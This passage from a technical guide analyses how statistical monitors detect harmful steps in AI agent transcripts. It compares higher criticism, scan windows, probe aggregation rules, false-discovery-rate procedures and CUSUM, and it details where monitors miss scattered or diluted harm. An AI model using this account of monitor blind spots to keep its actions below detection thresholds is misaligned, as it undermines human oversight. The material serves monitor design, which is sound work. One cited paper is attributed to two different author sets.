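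Steps also differ in length, and a long step may give a monitor more evidence than a short one. In *Thresholding the Higher Criticism Test Statistic for Optimality in a Heterogeneous Setting*, Chan (2023) studied comparisons with unequal amounts of data and found that dropping those with the least data improved both higher criticism and the test based on the smallest p-value. But in the running example, the evidence in step 612 takes up only 200 tokens, so a minimum length could remove the step that matters. Chan's statistic reduces this risk by trying several minimum sizes, including no minimum.

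### Detecting harm without locating it

A team can have good evidence that a transcript contains harm without knowing which steps are harmful. In the example with 40 weak steps, detecting harm theoretically requires a shift of 1.4, while locating the harmful steps requires about 3.3. The second figure comes from *r* = *b*, where a cut-off can flag many of the harmful steps and few clean ones.

If the cut-off equals the shift, about half of the harmful steps cross it. At a cut-off of 1.4, about 800 clean steps cross along with those 20 harmful ones, but at 3.3 only about five do. Donoho and Jin place the stronger signals in a separate "estimable" region. Kotekal (2021), in *Statistical Limits of Sparse Mixture Detection*, also distinguishes finding the individual signals from detecting that there are any.

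Between the two limits, an imperfect list can still save a reviewer a lot of work. At a shift of 2.5, a cut-off of 2.5 leaves about 82 steps to read instead of 10,000, and 20 of those 82 are harmful.

Kashtan and Kipnis (2023), in *An Information-Theoretic Approach for Detecting Edits in AI-Generated Text*, used higher criticism to detect whether a person had changed a few sentences in an article written by a language model, and to locate those sentences. They measured how improbable each sentence's words were to a language model, since human sentences tend to be less predictable. They then computed a p-value for each sentence by comparing it with AI-written sentences of the same length, and combined the p-values with higher criticism.

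If the statistic was high enough, Kashtan and Kipnis listed every sentence with a p-value at or below the cut-off that produced the maximum. The list for an article about Welsh corgis included a sentence with a p-value of 0.21, which would be unremarkable alone. They stress that a sentence is listed because of the pattern across the whole article. The same caution applies to a list of suspicious steps, because the evidence that the transcript contains harm may be strong even when the evidence against any one step is weak.

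The method left out sentences of about ten tokens or fewer because the measure didn't work on them. A monitor that scores steps by how improbable their text is could have a similar problem with short shell commands.

### Scanning for a run of suspicious tokens

Higher criticism ignores the order of the scores. If harmful tokens are next to each other, a scan statistic can use this by averaging the scores inside a window that slides along the transcript and keeping the highest average.

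In the running example, suppose each of the 200 harmful tokens scores 0.5 standard deviations higher than a clean one. A window covering exactly those tokens has a z-score of 0.5 × √200, or 7.1. Kou and Walther (2019), in *Large-Scale inference with block structure*, give the asymptotic threshold for a window of length *L* as

√(2 ln(*n*/*L*)).

For *n* = 500,000 and *L* = 200, this is 4.0, so the window stands out clearly. Even if the team treated all 500,000 window positions as separate tests and allowed a 1% false positive rate, the threshold would be about 5.5 and recall would be 94%.

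A search for the highest single token would miss the same span, because a token needs a score of about 5.1 to stand out among 500,000 and the highest of the 200 harmful tokens would typically score about 3.3. Higher criticism applied to tokens would need each harmful token's score to be shifted by about 1.6, compared with 0.28 for the scan.

The scan has this advantage only if the window fits the span reasonably well.

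| Window length in tokens | Best z-score expected for a window on the span | Threshold |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.5 | 5.1 |
| 10 | 1.6 | 4.7 |
| 40 | 3.2 | 4.3 |
| 200 | 7.1 | 4.0 |
| 1,000 | 3.2 | 3.5 |

The middle column gives the average score for one window in the best position. The highest score among several short windows inside the span would be somewhat larger, but still not enough at ten tokens.

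When the length is unknown, a team can try several. Trying every possible start and end would mean testing about 125 billion windows for 500,000 tokens. Kou and Walther describe a much smaller set that approximates all of them, whose size grows only slightly faster than the number of tokens, *n*. Short windows are more numerous, so one of them is more likely to score high by chance. To correct for this, they subtract √(2 ln(e*n*/*L*)) from each window's z-score before comparing lengths, where *L* is the window's length and e is about 2.72.

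For harm that comes in several short runs, Kou and Walther propose structured higher criticism, which applies higher criticism to window scores instead of individual scores. If the 40 weak steps came in eight runs of five, the theoretical boundary would fall from 1.4 to about 0.8 standard deviations per step. In one of their simulations, 10,000 scores contained about four runs of six. Ordinary higher criticism had almost no power, even for strong signals, while the structured version had the highest power of the four methods tested.

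Locating a single harmful run is no harder than detecting it, so a scan that detects the harmful 200 tokens also shows the reviewer roughly where to look. If there are several runs, Kou and Walther's calculations indicate that finding all of them takes a stronger signal than detecting that some exist.

### What correlated tokens and heavy tails change

These figures assume independent, normally distributed scores. But the scores of neighbouring tokens tend to rise and fall together, so a window of 200 tokens contains less evidence than 200 independent scores would. If neighbouring scores have a correlation of 0.5 that fades with distance, the window's z-score falls from 7.1 to 4.1, barely above the threshold. With a correlation of 0.9, it falls to 1.7, which is too low for the scan to detect.

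Ignoring the correlation between tokens increases false positives. If an engineer calculates z-scores as though tokens were independent when their correlation is 0.5, about 27 of 2,500 separate clean windows will exceed the threshold of 4.0. The expected number would be 0.1 if the tokens were independent.

Differences between whole sessions are a bigger problem for rules that count high scores than for rules that use the highest score. Suppose every step in a clean security session of 10,000 steps scores 0.5 higher than usual. The rule that flags a session with seven or more scores above 3.5 would wrongly flag it 98% of the time, and the rule based on the highest score would do so about 10% of the time. Subtracting each transcript's median score from its step scores would remove such a shift, and a few harmful steps barely change the median.

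Kashtan and Kipnis report that short-range dependence between sentences has little effect on the critical values of higher criticism, but that other kinds of dependence can reduce the test's power. They recommend using complete clean documents to set the threshold where possible.

When clean scores have heavy tails, meaning that extreme scores are more common than in a normal distribution, the shift needed to detect a harmful step grows faster with transcript length. Donoho and Jin also analysed one such distribution, the double exponential. If clean scores follow it, one harmful step needs a shift of about 4.9 standard deviations among 1,000 steps and 9.8 among a million, compared with 3.7 and 5.3 for normal scores.

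The choice of statistic also matters more. For 40 harmful steps among 10,000, the theoretical requirement becomes 1.3 standard deviations for higher criticism and 3.9 for the highest score, because the most extreme scores often come from clean steps. But if a team calculates p-values from a normal curve when the real tails are heavier, clean transcripts will contain far too many small p-values, and higher criticism would flag those transcripts.

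### Probe designs on prompts of 900,000 tokens

A probe that scores every token needs a rule for combining the scores, and the common designs correspond closely to the statistics above. Google DeepMind's *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (January 2026) compared several of them at detecting requests for help with cyberattacks in prompts to Gemini 2.5 Flash.

The researchers trained most of the probes only on shorter prompts, then tested them on prompts averaging more than 900,000 tokens. They made these long prompts by surrounding a request with code from software projects, and placed harmful requests at the beginning, at the end or just before the last project.

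| Probe | How it combines token scores | Clean long prompts flagged | Harmful long prompts missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mean | Average of all tokens | 0.5% | 99.1% |
| Attention | Average with learned softmax weights | 0.0% | 87.9% |
| Moving average | Highest value of a running average that favours recent tokens | 13.6% | 1.7% |
| MultiMax | Highest token score for each of several heads, added together | 7.8% | 0.4% |
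| Maximum of rolling means | Highest weighted average over ten tokens | 1.2% | 3.0% |
| Attention, also trained on long prompts | Average with learned softmax weights | 1.2% | 1.3% |

The mean and attention probes missed most of the harmful requests, as dilution predicts. The study describes the attention probe's problem as too many false positives on long prompts, but in its results, the version trained on shorter prompts had no false positives and missed 88% of the attacks.

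Designs based on a maximum rarely missed an attack, but longer prompts gave them more chances of a false positive. MultiMax flagged 0.3% of ordinary short prompts and 7.8% of long ones. A version with 20 heads flagged 1.1% and 82%, respectively. The moving average gives half of its weight to the current token, a quarter to the one before and so on. This smooths the scores about as much as averaging three tokens, so one or two high-scoring tokens can still trigger a flag.

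The maximum of rolling means is a scan statistic with a fixed window and learned weights, and it kept both error rates low. Its ten-token window would be too short for the running example if every harmful token scored only 0.5 higher. Its 97% recall on long prompts suggests that the harmful requests contained short stretches with scores raised by much more than 0.5.

The researchers chose one threshold for each probe on shorter validation prompts and used it at all lengths. The comparison therefore measures both how well each design separates harmful prompts from clean ones and how well its threshold carries over to long prompts. A higher threshold for long prompts would reduce MultiMax's false positives and might lower its recall only slightly. It could not help the mean probe, which already flagged almost nothing.

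Training on long prompts also solved most of the problem for the attention probe, but it increased the cost of training 22-fold. AlphaEvolve, Google DeepMind's system for automatically improving programs, tried about 2,500 designs and found a cheaper alternative, a variant of MultiMax trained without long prompts. This variant flagged 1.7% of clean long prompts and missed 4.8% of harmful ones. Across all the test sets, it and the two best rolling designs performed too similarly to rank. The study covered only users' prompts, so it offers no direct evidence about harmful steps in an agent's own work.

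### When averaging works better

On short texts, the ranking can reverse. McKenzie, Pawar and colleagues (2025), in *Detecting High-Stakes Interactions with Activation Probes*, tested six ways of combining token scores from Llama 3.3 70B to recognise conversations where a bad answer could cause serious harm, such as requests for medical advice. Attention, softmax and mean probes did best overall. The softmax probe computes its weights from the token scores, so its result lies between their average and their maximum.

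The maximum score and the maximum 40-token rolling mean did nearly as well only on a set of medical texts. McKenzie and colleagues think that many tokens in a conversation contribute to whether the stakes are high, whereas a few words may decide it in the medical texts. In terms of the mixture model, most of these conversations have many shifted scores, and averaging is the right choice when more than about √*n* of the *n* scores are shifted.

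At a false positive rate of 1%, the best probe detected 43% of the high-stakes conversations and the best language model monitor detected 55%. If those rates held on agent transcripts with a base rate of 0.1%, precision would be about 4% for the probe and 5% for the monitor. McKenzie and colleagues suggest using probes as a first filter and having a language model check the uncertain cases.

*Measuring Concept Content in Text from LLM Activations* (2026) found a similar split when measuring how much company texts say about environmental, social and governance topics. Reading only the last token worked best for the environmental task. Taking the maximum worked best for the social and governance tasks, where the relevant signals may be few but strong.

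How a probe is trained also matters. In *Do Probing and Steering Favor the Same Directions* (2026), probes trained on the last token of a text did worse in all six comparisons when the researchers used the highest token score instead of the last token's score, with AUROC falling by up to 0.10. The probes had never learned to give low scores to ordinary tokens in the middle of a text, so the maximum picked up their errors. Similarly, in the Gemini study, a probe trained with attention but used with MultiMax flagged 44% of clean long prompts, compared with 7.8% for a probe trained with MultiMax.

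### False positives from single words

Taking the maximum score also makes a probe sensitive to isolated words. A biologist's harmless question may name a dangerous pathogen, and one high-scoring token is enough to flag it. He, Sel and colleagues (2026), in *Segment-Level Coherence for Robust Harmful Intent Probing in LLMs*, found that this problem persisted even when the training data contained many harmless scientific conversations.

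Their probe first averages the scores in every window of 16 tokens. It then averages the eight highest window scores instead of relying mainly on the highest. During training, a penalty discourages uneven scores among the suspicious parts of harmless conversations. At a false positive rate of 1%, the method's recall was 36% higher in relative terms than that of strong earlier probes that also work while the text is being written.

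The eight windows the formula requires can all fit into a stretch of 23 tokens, because windows that start one token apart share 15 of their 16 tokens. A short run of high scores is therefore enough, even without evidence from other parts of the conversation. This suits step 612, where all the evidence is in one place. To combine distant steps, such as three payments of $3,100, a team would have to take the highest-scoring window from each step and then count or average across steps.

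The gain also depended on the task. He and colleagues saw the clearest improvements on conversations about biological and chemical weapons, which averaged about 3,000 tokens. On general high-stakes texts of about 300 tokens, the method beat the most similar earlier probe by at most about 1 percentage point and sometimes did slightly worse than the best alternative.

### Running several tests at once

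A team rarely knows in advance whether a harmful transcript will contain one blatant command, a run of weakly suspicious tokens or 40 small thefts. It can run a separate test for each pattern and flag the transcript if any test raises an alarm, as long as it divides the permitted false positive rate among the tests.

Using both tests only slightly reduces sensitivity to a single harmful step. Suppose a team allows a total false positive rate of 1% and gives half to the highest step score and half to higher criticism. Among 1,000 steps, a single harmful step then needs a shift of 5.7 rather than 5.5 standard deviations for 90% recall. The monitor can also detect groups of weaker steps that the highest score would miss. If the two tests tend to flag the same clean transcripts, the total false positive rate will be below 1%, and the team could lower both thresholds slightly by calibrating on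 whole clean transcripts.

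## Setting a threshold for thousands of comparisons

For a single test, a team can set a threshold directly on the p-value. With 1,000 steps per transcript and 10,000 transcripts a day, the team also has to decide which false alarms to count and over which set of tests.

### Two error rates

Suppose a procedure flags *R* items, *V* of which are clean. The two most common error rates are

family-wise error rate = P(*V* ≥ 1)

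false discovery rate (FDR) = average of *V* / max(*R*, 1).

The maximum in the second formula makes the share zero when the procedure flags nothing. If a procedure flags 20 steps and two of them are clean, the result counts as a failure in the family-wise rate, just as it would if all 20 were clean, but as 10% in the FDR.

Benjamini and Hochberg (1995), in *Controlling the False Discovery Rate*, proposed the FDR because controlling the family-wise error rate is often stricter than necessary. Family-wise control matters when a single error would invalidate the overall conclusion. In screening, such as selecting transcripts for a review queue, a few false leads do little harm, but too many burden the follow-up work. The FDR is never higher than the family-wise error rate, so any procedure that limits the family-wise error rate also limits the FDR.

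### Three procedures on one transcript

Suppose the four smallest p-values in a transcript of 1,000 steps are 0.00002, 0.00015, 0.00028 and 0.0005, and the team chooses a level of 0.10.

The Bonferroni procedure divides the significance level by the number of tests. With a level of 0.10 and 1,000 tests, it flags every p-value at or below 0.0001. Each test then has at most a 0.01% chance of a false flag, so the chance of any false flag across all 1,000 tests is at most 10%.

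The Benjamini-Hochberg (BH) procedure controls the FDR in four steps:

1. Sort the p-values from smallest to largest.
2. Give the *i*-th smallest a line of *i* × 0.10/1,000.
3. Find the highest rank whose p-value is at or below its line.
4. Flag that step and every step with a smaller p-value.

The Benjamini-Yekutieli (BY) procedure works like BH but divides each BH threshold by 1 + 1/2 + 1/3 + … + 1/1,000, which is about 7.49.

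| Rank | p-value | Bonferroni line | BH line | BY line |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.00002 | 0.0001 | 0.0001 | 0.000013 |
| 2 | 0.00015 | 0.0001 | 0.0002 | 0.000027 |
| 3 | 0.00028 | 0.0001 | 0.0003 | 0.000040 |
| 4 | 0.0005 | 0.0001 | 0.0004 | 0.000053 |
| Steps flagged | | 1 | 3 | 0 |

All the other p-values lie above their BH lines. BH would still flag the second step if its p-value were 0.00025, which is above its line, because the third p-value is below its line.

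The BH lines come from an estimate of the share of flags that are false alarms. If the team flags every step with a p-value up to 0.00028, it can expect at most 0.28 false flags among 1,000 clean steps. Three steps meet that cut-off, so the estimated share is 0.28/3, or 9%. Raising the cut-off to 0.0005 would flag four steps and bring the estimate to 0.5/4, or 12.5%, which is above the chosen level. Benjamini and Hochberg show that their procedure flags as many items as possible while keeping this estimate within the chosen level.

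BH improves on Bonferroni only when several p-values are small. If step 612 is the only suspicious step in the running example, both methods require its p-value to be 0.0001 or less. *A Uniform Improvement of the Benjamini-Hochberg Procedure via e-Closure* (Goeman, 2026) presents "closed BH", which never flags fewer items than BH. On a set of 4,289 p-values, it raised the number flagged at the 5% level from 767 to 801. But closed BH doesn't make a lone suspicious step easier to detect, because it flags nothing when BH flags nothing. Its gain is also negligible when the number of flags is below the square root of the number of tests, which is about 32 for 1,000 steps.

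### What each procedure assumes about dependence

Bonferroni works under any dependence, because the chance of at least one false alarm never exceeds the sum of the chances at each step. BH needs stronger assumptions. Its original proof covered independent tests, and *The control of the false discovery rate in multiple testing under dependency* (Benjamini and Yekutieli, 2001) extended it to a form of positive dependence. Roughly, a low p-value at one clean step must never make low p-values at other steps less likely. Normally distributed scores meet this condition if no clean step's score is negatively correlated with any other step's score. An agent that keeps retrying an odd command probably produces such scores.

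P-values that share a calibration set also depend on each other, because a set with unusually low clean scores lowers all of them at once. Bates and colleagues proved that this dependence is the permitted kind.

The condition can fail when a higher score for one step means lower scores for others, as when a monitor has to divide 100 points of suspicion among the steps. BY covers such cases because its threshold is strict enough for the worst possible dependence, under which ordinary BH at 10% could have an FDR of up to 75% with 1,000 tests. Benjamini and Yekutieli note that the distributions that reach this kind of bound are bizarre and rare in practice. Goeman simulated 200 tests with correlations of up to 0.9, including a type of test that violates the condition, and the FDR of BH stayed below its 5% target.

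The Benjamini-Yekutieli (BY) procedure is a poor choice for detecting a lone harmful step. Bonferroni is also valid under any dependence between tests, and BY's threshold is looser than Bonferroni's only from the eighth-smallest p-value on.

Even when BH's guarantee holds, dependence affects how false alarms are spread across transcripts. The FDR is an average, so an FDR of 10% across 100 clean transcripts could mean that 90 have no flags and 10 have 50 flags each.

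### BH inside every transcript

When harm is rare, a team that runs BH separately on each transcript will find that far fewer of its flags are correct than the 90% or so it might expect. Every flag in a clean transcript is false, so even one flag makes the share of false alarms 100%. The FDR for such a transcript therefore equals the chance of any flag, which is the family-wise error rate.

The company with 10,000 transcripts a day has 9,990 clean ones. If their steps are independent, BH at 10% flags at least one step in about 999 of them. Even if it also flags all ten harmful transcripts, 99% of the transcripts in the review queue are clean.

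The guarantee still holds across all 10,000 transcripts. The average share of false alarms is about 10%, because about 9,000 transcripts have no flags and count as zero. But reviewers see only the flagged transcripts. Benjamini and Bogomolov (2011) analyse this problem for grouped data in *Adjusting for selection bias in testing multiple families of hypotheses*. In one example, each of 100 groups has two tests with no real effect. Researchers look only at groups with at least one p-value below 0.05 and apply Bonferroni at 5% within each. The average family-wise error rate among the selected groups is 51%.

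Benjamini and Yekutieli point out that controlling the FDR within each group also controls it overall if the groups are large and contain some real effects. Clean transcripts contain no real effects, so they don't meet the second condition. Efron (2008), in *Simultaneous inference*, defends separate analyses when each is expected to flag a reasonable number of cases, and suggests about ten. A transcript with one harmful step falls far short of that.

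### Pooling, two stages or a fixed number of reviews

The company can put all its steps into one BH analysis. If every transcript has 1,000 steps, the analysis has 10 million p-values, and the cut-off for the tenth-smallest p-value is 0.0000001. If ten steps are flagged at that cut-off, about one of them would be clean.

Applying Benjamini-Hochberg (BH) to individual steps limits the expected share of false flags among flagged steps, but the share of flagged transcripts that contain no harm can be much higher. Suppose the monitor catches 90 blatantly harmful steps, all in one run, and no other real harm. BH at 10% then allows about ten false flags elsewhere, probably in ten different transcripts. Reviewers would open 11 transcripts and find no harm in ten of them, even though 90% of the flagged steps are harmful.

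Pooling also assumes that p-values mean the same thing everywhere. Efron compared brain scans of six children with dyslexia and six without at 15,443 locations. A pooled analysis at 10% flagged 198 locations, nine of them in the back half of the brain. Separate analyses flagged 281 in the front half and none in the back. Scores were higher than usual throughout one region, and none of its locations stood out when Efron compared them with that region's own null distribution. Legitimate security work could cause the same problem in a pool of transcripts if its scores are also higher than usual throughout.

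The second option is to test transcripts first and steps second. The company computes one p-value per transcript, for example from its highest step score, and runs BH on the 10,000 results. The FDR then applies to the transcripts in the review queue. To make claims about individual steps, the company can use a correction by Benjamini and Bogomolov. If the first stage selects *R* of *m* transcripts, the second stage tests the steps in each at level *qR*/*m*, where *q* is the target. With ten transcripts selected and a target of 10%, that level is 0.0001. To be the only step flagged in its transcript, a step then needs a p-value of at most 0.0000001, the same as with pooling. If transcripts are independent, the correction keeps the expected share of false alarms among flagged steps, averaged over the selected transcripts, at or below 10%.

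The size of the calibration set limits this option. With 9,999 clean transcripts, the smallest possible p-value is 0.0001, so BH at 10% flags transcripts only if at least ten from that day score higher than every calibration transcript. To be able to flag just one transcript, the company needs about 100,000 clean ones.

The third option is to review a fixed number of transcripts each day, starting with the highest score. This requires only a ranking and keeps the workload constant, but it doesn't limit the share of false alarms. On a day without harm, every reviewed transcript is a false alarm. If the scores of clean transcripts drift upwards, harmful transcripts drop out of the queue while its length stays the same.

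The table compares these options when a harmful step scores 5.5 standard deviations above the clean average. In the previous section, this gap gave about 90% recall at a 1% false positive rate. All scores are independent and normally distributed, and each harmful transcript has one harmful step.

| Rule | Harmful transcripts flagged, out of 10 | Clean transcripts flagged |
|---|---|---|
| BH at 10% inside each transcript | almost 10 | 999 |
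| 1% false positive rate per transcript | 9 | 100 |
| 20 highest-scoring transcripts | 8 | 12 |
| BH at 10% across transcripts, or across all steps | 6 | fewer than 1 |

The company can choose how many top-ranked transcripts to read, such as 20, well only if it knows roughly how many harmful ones to expect. BH's threshold depends on the p-values, so BH flags more transcripts when an attack campaign produces 200 harmful ones in a day. Reading only the top 20 would miss at least 180 of them.

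The share of false alerts also depends on the period each analysis covers. A smaller company with 100 transcripts a day and the same base rate of 0.1% has a harmful transcript on about one day in ten. If it runs BH at 10% every evening for 100 days, it gets false alarms on about nine of the roughly 90 clean days, and at most about ten correct flags. Roughly half of its alerts are false, even though the FDR is 10% or less every day. Analysing all 100 days together would bring the share of false alerts close to 10%, but the company would learn of some harm three months late. Streaming procedures, covered in the next section, control error rates while results arrive one at a time.

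### e-values and the e-BH procedure

Evidence can also take the form of an e-value, a non-negative number whose average is at most 1 for clean steps. It is like the payout from a $1 bet that makes no profit on average when the step is clean, so a large payout is evidence that the step is not clean. A clean step has at most a 5% chance of getting an e-value of 20 or more.

Wang and Ramdas (2020) introduced e-BH, a version of BH for e-values, in *False discovery rate control with e-values*. For a target FDR of α, it sorts the e-values of *m* steps from largest to smallest, finds the largest *k* for which the *k*th e-value is at least *m*/(α*k*), and flags the top *k* steps.

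This procedure controls the FDR under any dependence, with no correction like BY's. Wang (2022), in *Elementary proofs of several results on false discovery rate*, gives a short proof:

1. If e-BH flags *R* steps, each has an e-value of at least *m*/(α*R*). Rearranged, 1/*R* is at most α/*m* times that e-value.
2. Each clean step among the flagged ones adds 1/*R* to the share of false alarms. The share is therefore at most α/*m* times the sum of the clean steps' e-values.
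3. Each of those e-values averages at most 1, and the average of a sum is the sum of the averages, however the values depend on each other. The FDR is therefore at most α times the proportion of clean steps.

The drawback of e-BH is that it requires very strong evidence. At level 0.10, a lone harmful step among 1,000 needs an e-value of at least 1,000/0.10, or 10,000, to be flagged. Two harmful steps need 5,000 each, and ten need 1,000 each.

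Some monitors can't produce e-values large enough for e-BH to flag a single step on its own. Dividing a monitor's score by its average score on clean steps gives a valid e-value. If scores run from 0 to 1 and average 0.001 on clean steps, the e-value can't exceed 1,000, so e-BH will flag either no steps or at least ten.

Converting p-values to e-values also loses power. Wang and Ramdas give general conditions for such conversions, and one standard formula is *κp*^(*κ*−1), with *κ* between 0 and 1. At *κ* = 0.5, an e-value of 10,000 requires a p-value of 0.0000000025. At *κ* = 0.1, it requires about 0.000003, still far below BH's 0.0001. An all-or-nothing conversion that gives 10,000 when *p* is at most 0.0001, and 0 otherwise, avoids this loss, but e-BH then becomes Bonferroni.

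The loss of recall is smaller if the team has a good model of harmful scores. It can then use the likelihood ratio, which divides the probability of a score if the step is harmful by its probability if the step is harmless. If harmful steps score 5.5 standard deviations higher on average, the ratio reaches 10,000 at a score of 4.4, compared with Bonferroni's threshold of 3.7. Recall within the transcript would be 86% at 4.4 and 96% at 3.7.

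*Boosting e-BH via conditional calibration* (2024) notes that the actual FDR of e-BH is often far below the target, so e-BH misses more than it has to. *Bringing closure to FDR control* (Xu, Fischer and Ramdas, 2025) presents a closed version that flags at least as much. It checks averages over groups of e-values instead of comparing each one with a fixed threshold. With e-values of 60, 39 and 11 and a level of 0.05, e-BH flags one item and the closed version flags all three. The gain is small for a lone harmful step. If each of the other 999 steps has an e-value of 1, the e-value it needs falls from 10,000 to 9,001.

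E-BH therefore offers no clear advantage over Bonferroni for step 612. E-values become more useful when evidence accumulates. The average of several e-values for the same step is still an e-value, even if the monitors that produced them make the same mistakes. Under suitable conditions, a team can also multiply e-values from successive tests.

### DISCO and the cost of controlling false findings

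The Google DeepMind study *Reliable Behavior Discovery via False Discovery Rate Control* (Madras, Wang and colleagues, 2026) shows how much such control can improve a search by language models. In the study, AI agents looked for patterns in the behaviour of other models. One of the five tasks was to find dishes for which a model writes longer recipes in French than in English. Another was to find when an image generator tends to produce cats of a certain colour.

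The study tests claims about a model's behaviour, not steps in a transcript, so its results don't directly measure how well a monitor finds harmful actions.

Five existing methods let the searching agent judge for itself which patterns were real. Their false discovery rates ranged from 0.4 to 0.95. The researchers estimated these rates by trying to replicate each finding with 100 new queries, because no list of true patterns exists.

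They then added e-BH, using half of the queries for the search and the other half to test the proposed patterns on new data. This brought the average FDR down to around the 10% target, although some tasks still exceeded it. It also reduced the number of true findings by 36% for the same total number of queries.

Part of that loss comes from having to fix the maximum number of hypotheses beforehand. If an agent allows for 100 hypotheses and tests only 20, e-BH requires five times as much evidence as it would for 20. The researchers' own method, DISCO, uses the number of hypotheses actually tested. To keep the guarantee, it limits the information from earlier results that the search can use, and stops testing a hypothesis once its e-value gets high enough or it has used up its rounds. DISCO made more true discoveries than the other methods with the same guarantee.

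*Structural Enforcement of Statistical Rigor in AI-Driven Discovery* (Sargsyan, 2025) reports a simulation in which an automated researcher tested 2,000 hypotheses at a fixed 5% level and had a false discovery rate of 41%. A streaming procedure lowered the rate to about 1%, against a target of 5%.

The two-stage design would also work well for auditing an agent. An auditor could hypothesize from old transcripts that the agent copies password files whenever a guide mentions a settings file, then test this in new runs. But the agent took step 612 only once, so there are no new data on that step, and rerunning the monitor would only reassess the same evidence.

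### When harms differ greatly in cost

The FDR counts all false alarms equally and does not account for missed harm. But controlling it doesn't require estimating how much damage a leak or a deleted database would do, and reviewers can understand a limit on the expected share of flags that are false. A team can later compare that limit with the precision it measures in practice, as the section on review load describes.

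But an FDR of 10% can be much too strict when missing a harmful transcript would do serious damage. In the table above, moving from BH across transcripts to a 1% false positive rate adds about 100 reviews and finds three more harmful transcripts. If a review costs $50, each extra find costs about $1,700, which is a low price for catching a leak of live passwords but a high one for catching a breach of a formatting rule. Moving from there to BH inside each transcript would take more than 1,000 extra reviews for each additional harmful transcript found.

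The company could also set the level above 10%. With BH across transcripts at 90%, it would review roughly 90 transcripts a day and find about nine of the ten harmful ones. A higher level like this suits human review. If a flag automatically stops the agent or suspends an account, false alarms do more harm, and 10% or even a family-wise guarantee may be appropriate.

A single FDR level works less well when one queue mixes serious and trivial harms. Suppose a monitor correctly flags 90 cases of agents writing to the wrong folder and wrongly flags ten cases of theft. The FDR is 10%, but every theft alert is false. The 90 easy folder cases also loosened the threshold for flagging theft.

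Running a separate analysis for each type of harm avoids this, and Efron's argument supports doing that for common types. But if a type occurs only once a month, most analyses of it would contain no real case, so most of the alerts could again be false. For rare types, it makes more sense to base the threshold on the effort a review takes and the harm a miss would cause.

Another option is the weighted BH procedure that Efron mentions, which is for classes of tests with different prior chances of a real effect. It can divide each p-value by a weight, as long as the weights average 1 and the team sets them without looking at the p-values. If 50 of the 1,000 steps send data outside the company and get a weight of 10, the other 950 get about 0.53. For a step to be the only one flagged, it then needs a p-value of at most 0.001 if it sends data out and about 0.00005 if it doesn't, compared with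 0.0001 without weights. Step 612 would be easier to detect, but a deleted database would be harder to detect.

Weighting errors by their seriousness changes the error rate itself. A weighted FDR is the expected share of false alarms when alerts in serious categories count for more. If a theft alert counts ten times as much as a folder alert, the share in the mixed queue is 100/190, or 53%, which makes the problem visible. *Bringing Closure to False Discovery Rate Control* (Xu, Solari and colleagues, 2025) provides a general theory for procedures that limit an expected loss. The loss only has to be non-negative, and zero when there are no flags or no clean items. A weighted share of false alarms meets these conditions, so the theory should cover it.

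For some procedures, the theory also lets a team wait until it has seen the data to choose which error rate to control. For instance, the team could switch to a family-wise guarantee when only a few strong flags appear. But even a weighted FDR does not penalize misses. A monitor that flags nothing has an FDR of zero under any weights, so the team still has to set a minimum recall for the harms it most wants to catch.

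## Raising an alarm while the agent is still running

BH and higher criticism need every p-value before they can flag anything. By the time the running example's transcript is complete, the password file has been on the outside machine for 388 steps. To prevent the leak, a monitor has to flag the command after the agent proposes it and before it runs. *StepSafe* (2026) trains monitors to judge proposed actions and scores them on this timing. An alarm counts as prevention only if it comes no later than the last step at which someone could have stopped the harm.

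### Looking again after every step

A live monitor repeatedly tests the same growing record. Suppose an engineer adds up the scores so far and applies an ordinary two-sided 5% test to the total after each step. If the scores are clean and independent, the chance of at least one false alarm is 5% after one step, about 19% after ten and about 53% after 1,000. *Self-Evolving Agents with Anytime-Valid Certificates* (2026) gives the general rule that a test designed for a fixed amount of data stops being valid once someone can check the result and decide whether to continue.

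The team also doesn't know in advance how many steps there will be, so it can't divide its error rate among them as the Bonferroni correction does. While the team waits for more evidence, the agent keeps working and may do more harm.

The section on calibration describes a threshold based on the highest step score in each clean transcript. This threshold still works while the agent is running, because a live monitor can raise the alarm as soon as a step's score crosses it. But this rule can't add up weak evidence from several steps.

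### CUSUM

CUSUM, short for cumulative sum, does add it up. The statistician E. S. Page introduced it in 1954. After each step *t*, it updates a running total:

*S*ₜ = max(0, *S*ₜ₋₁ + ln(probability of the score if harmful / probability if clean)).

The logarithm is positive when a score is more typical of harmful steps and negative when it is more typical of clean ones. The monitor raises an alarm when *S* reaches a threshold *h*. Because *S* never falls below zero, a long clean stretch can't build up a deficit that later evidence of harm would have to overcome.

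If harmful steps score 2 standard deviations higher than clean ones and scores are normally distributed, the logarithm is twice the score minus 2.

| Step | Score | Log likelihood ratio | *S* |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.4 | −1.2 | 0 |
| 2 | 1.3 | 0.6 | 0.6 |
| 3 | −0.2 | −2.4 | 0 |
| 4 | 2.6 | 3.2 | 3.2 |
| 5 | 1.7 | 1.4 | 4.6 |
| 6 | 2.9 | 3.8 | 8.4 |

The average run length is the average number of clean steps before a false alarm. *Online Change-Point Detection with Persistent Laplacian Features* (2026) includes a proof that a threshold of *h* makes it at least e^*h*. The average delay after harm begins is then roughly

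delay ≈ ln(average run length) / information per step,

where the information is the average log likelihood ratio of a harmful step, measured in nats. One nat of evidence multiplies the likelihood ratio by about 2.7. No method can do much better than this delay when the average run length is long.

For one false alarm per million steps, the evidence has to total ln(1,000,000), or 13.8 nats. If each of the company's 10,000 daily transcripts had 1,000 steps, that rate would produce about ten false alarms a day.

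| Shift of harmful steps, in standard deviations | Information per step | Harmful steps needed |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.5 nats | 28 |
| 2 | 2 nats | 7 |
| 3 | 4.5 nats | 3 |
| 5.3 | 14 nats | 1 |

*S* is usually close to zero when a harmful step arrives, so harm that lasts only one step has to raise it by nearly the full 13.8 nats. For step 612, CUSUM therefore amounts to a threshold on a single score and has no advantage over the simpler rule.

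CUSUM also helps little when the harmful steps are scattered. If 40 small thefts are spread over 10,000 steps, about 250 clean steps separate one from the next. With a shift of 2, each clean step lowers the total by 2 nats on average, so the evidence from one theft is gone long before the next.

The method works best when many suspicious steps occur in a row, but harmless retries produce the same pattern. If an agent repeats an odd command twelve times, the total rises twelve times, though the last eleven scores contain little new information. *Sequential statistical inference for Large Language Models* (2026) suggests looking for changes in how each score relates to the ones before it, which would discount such repeats.

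### How much time monitors get

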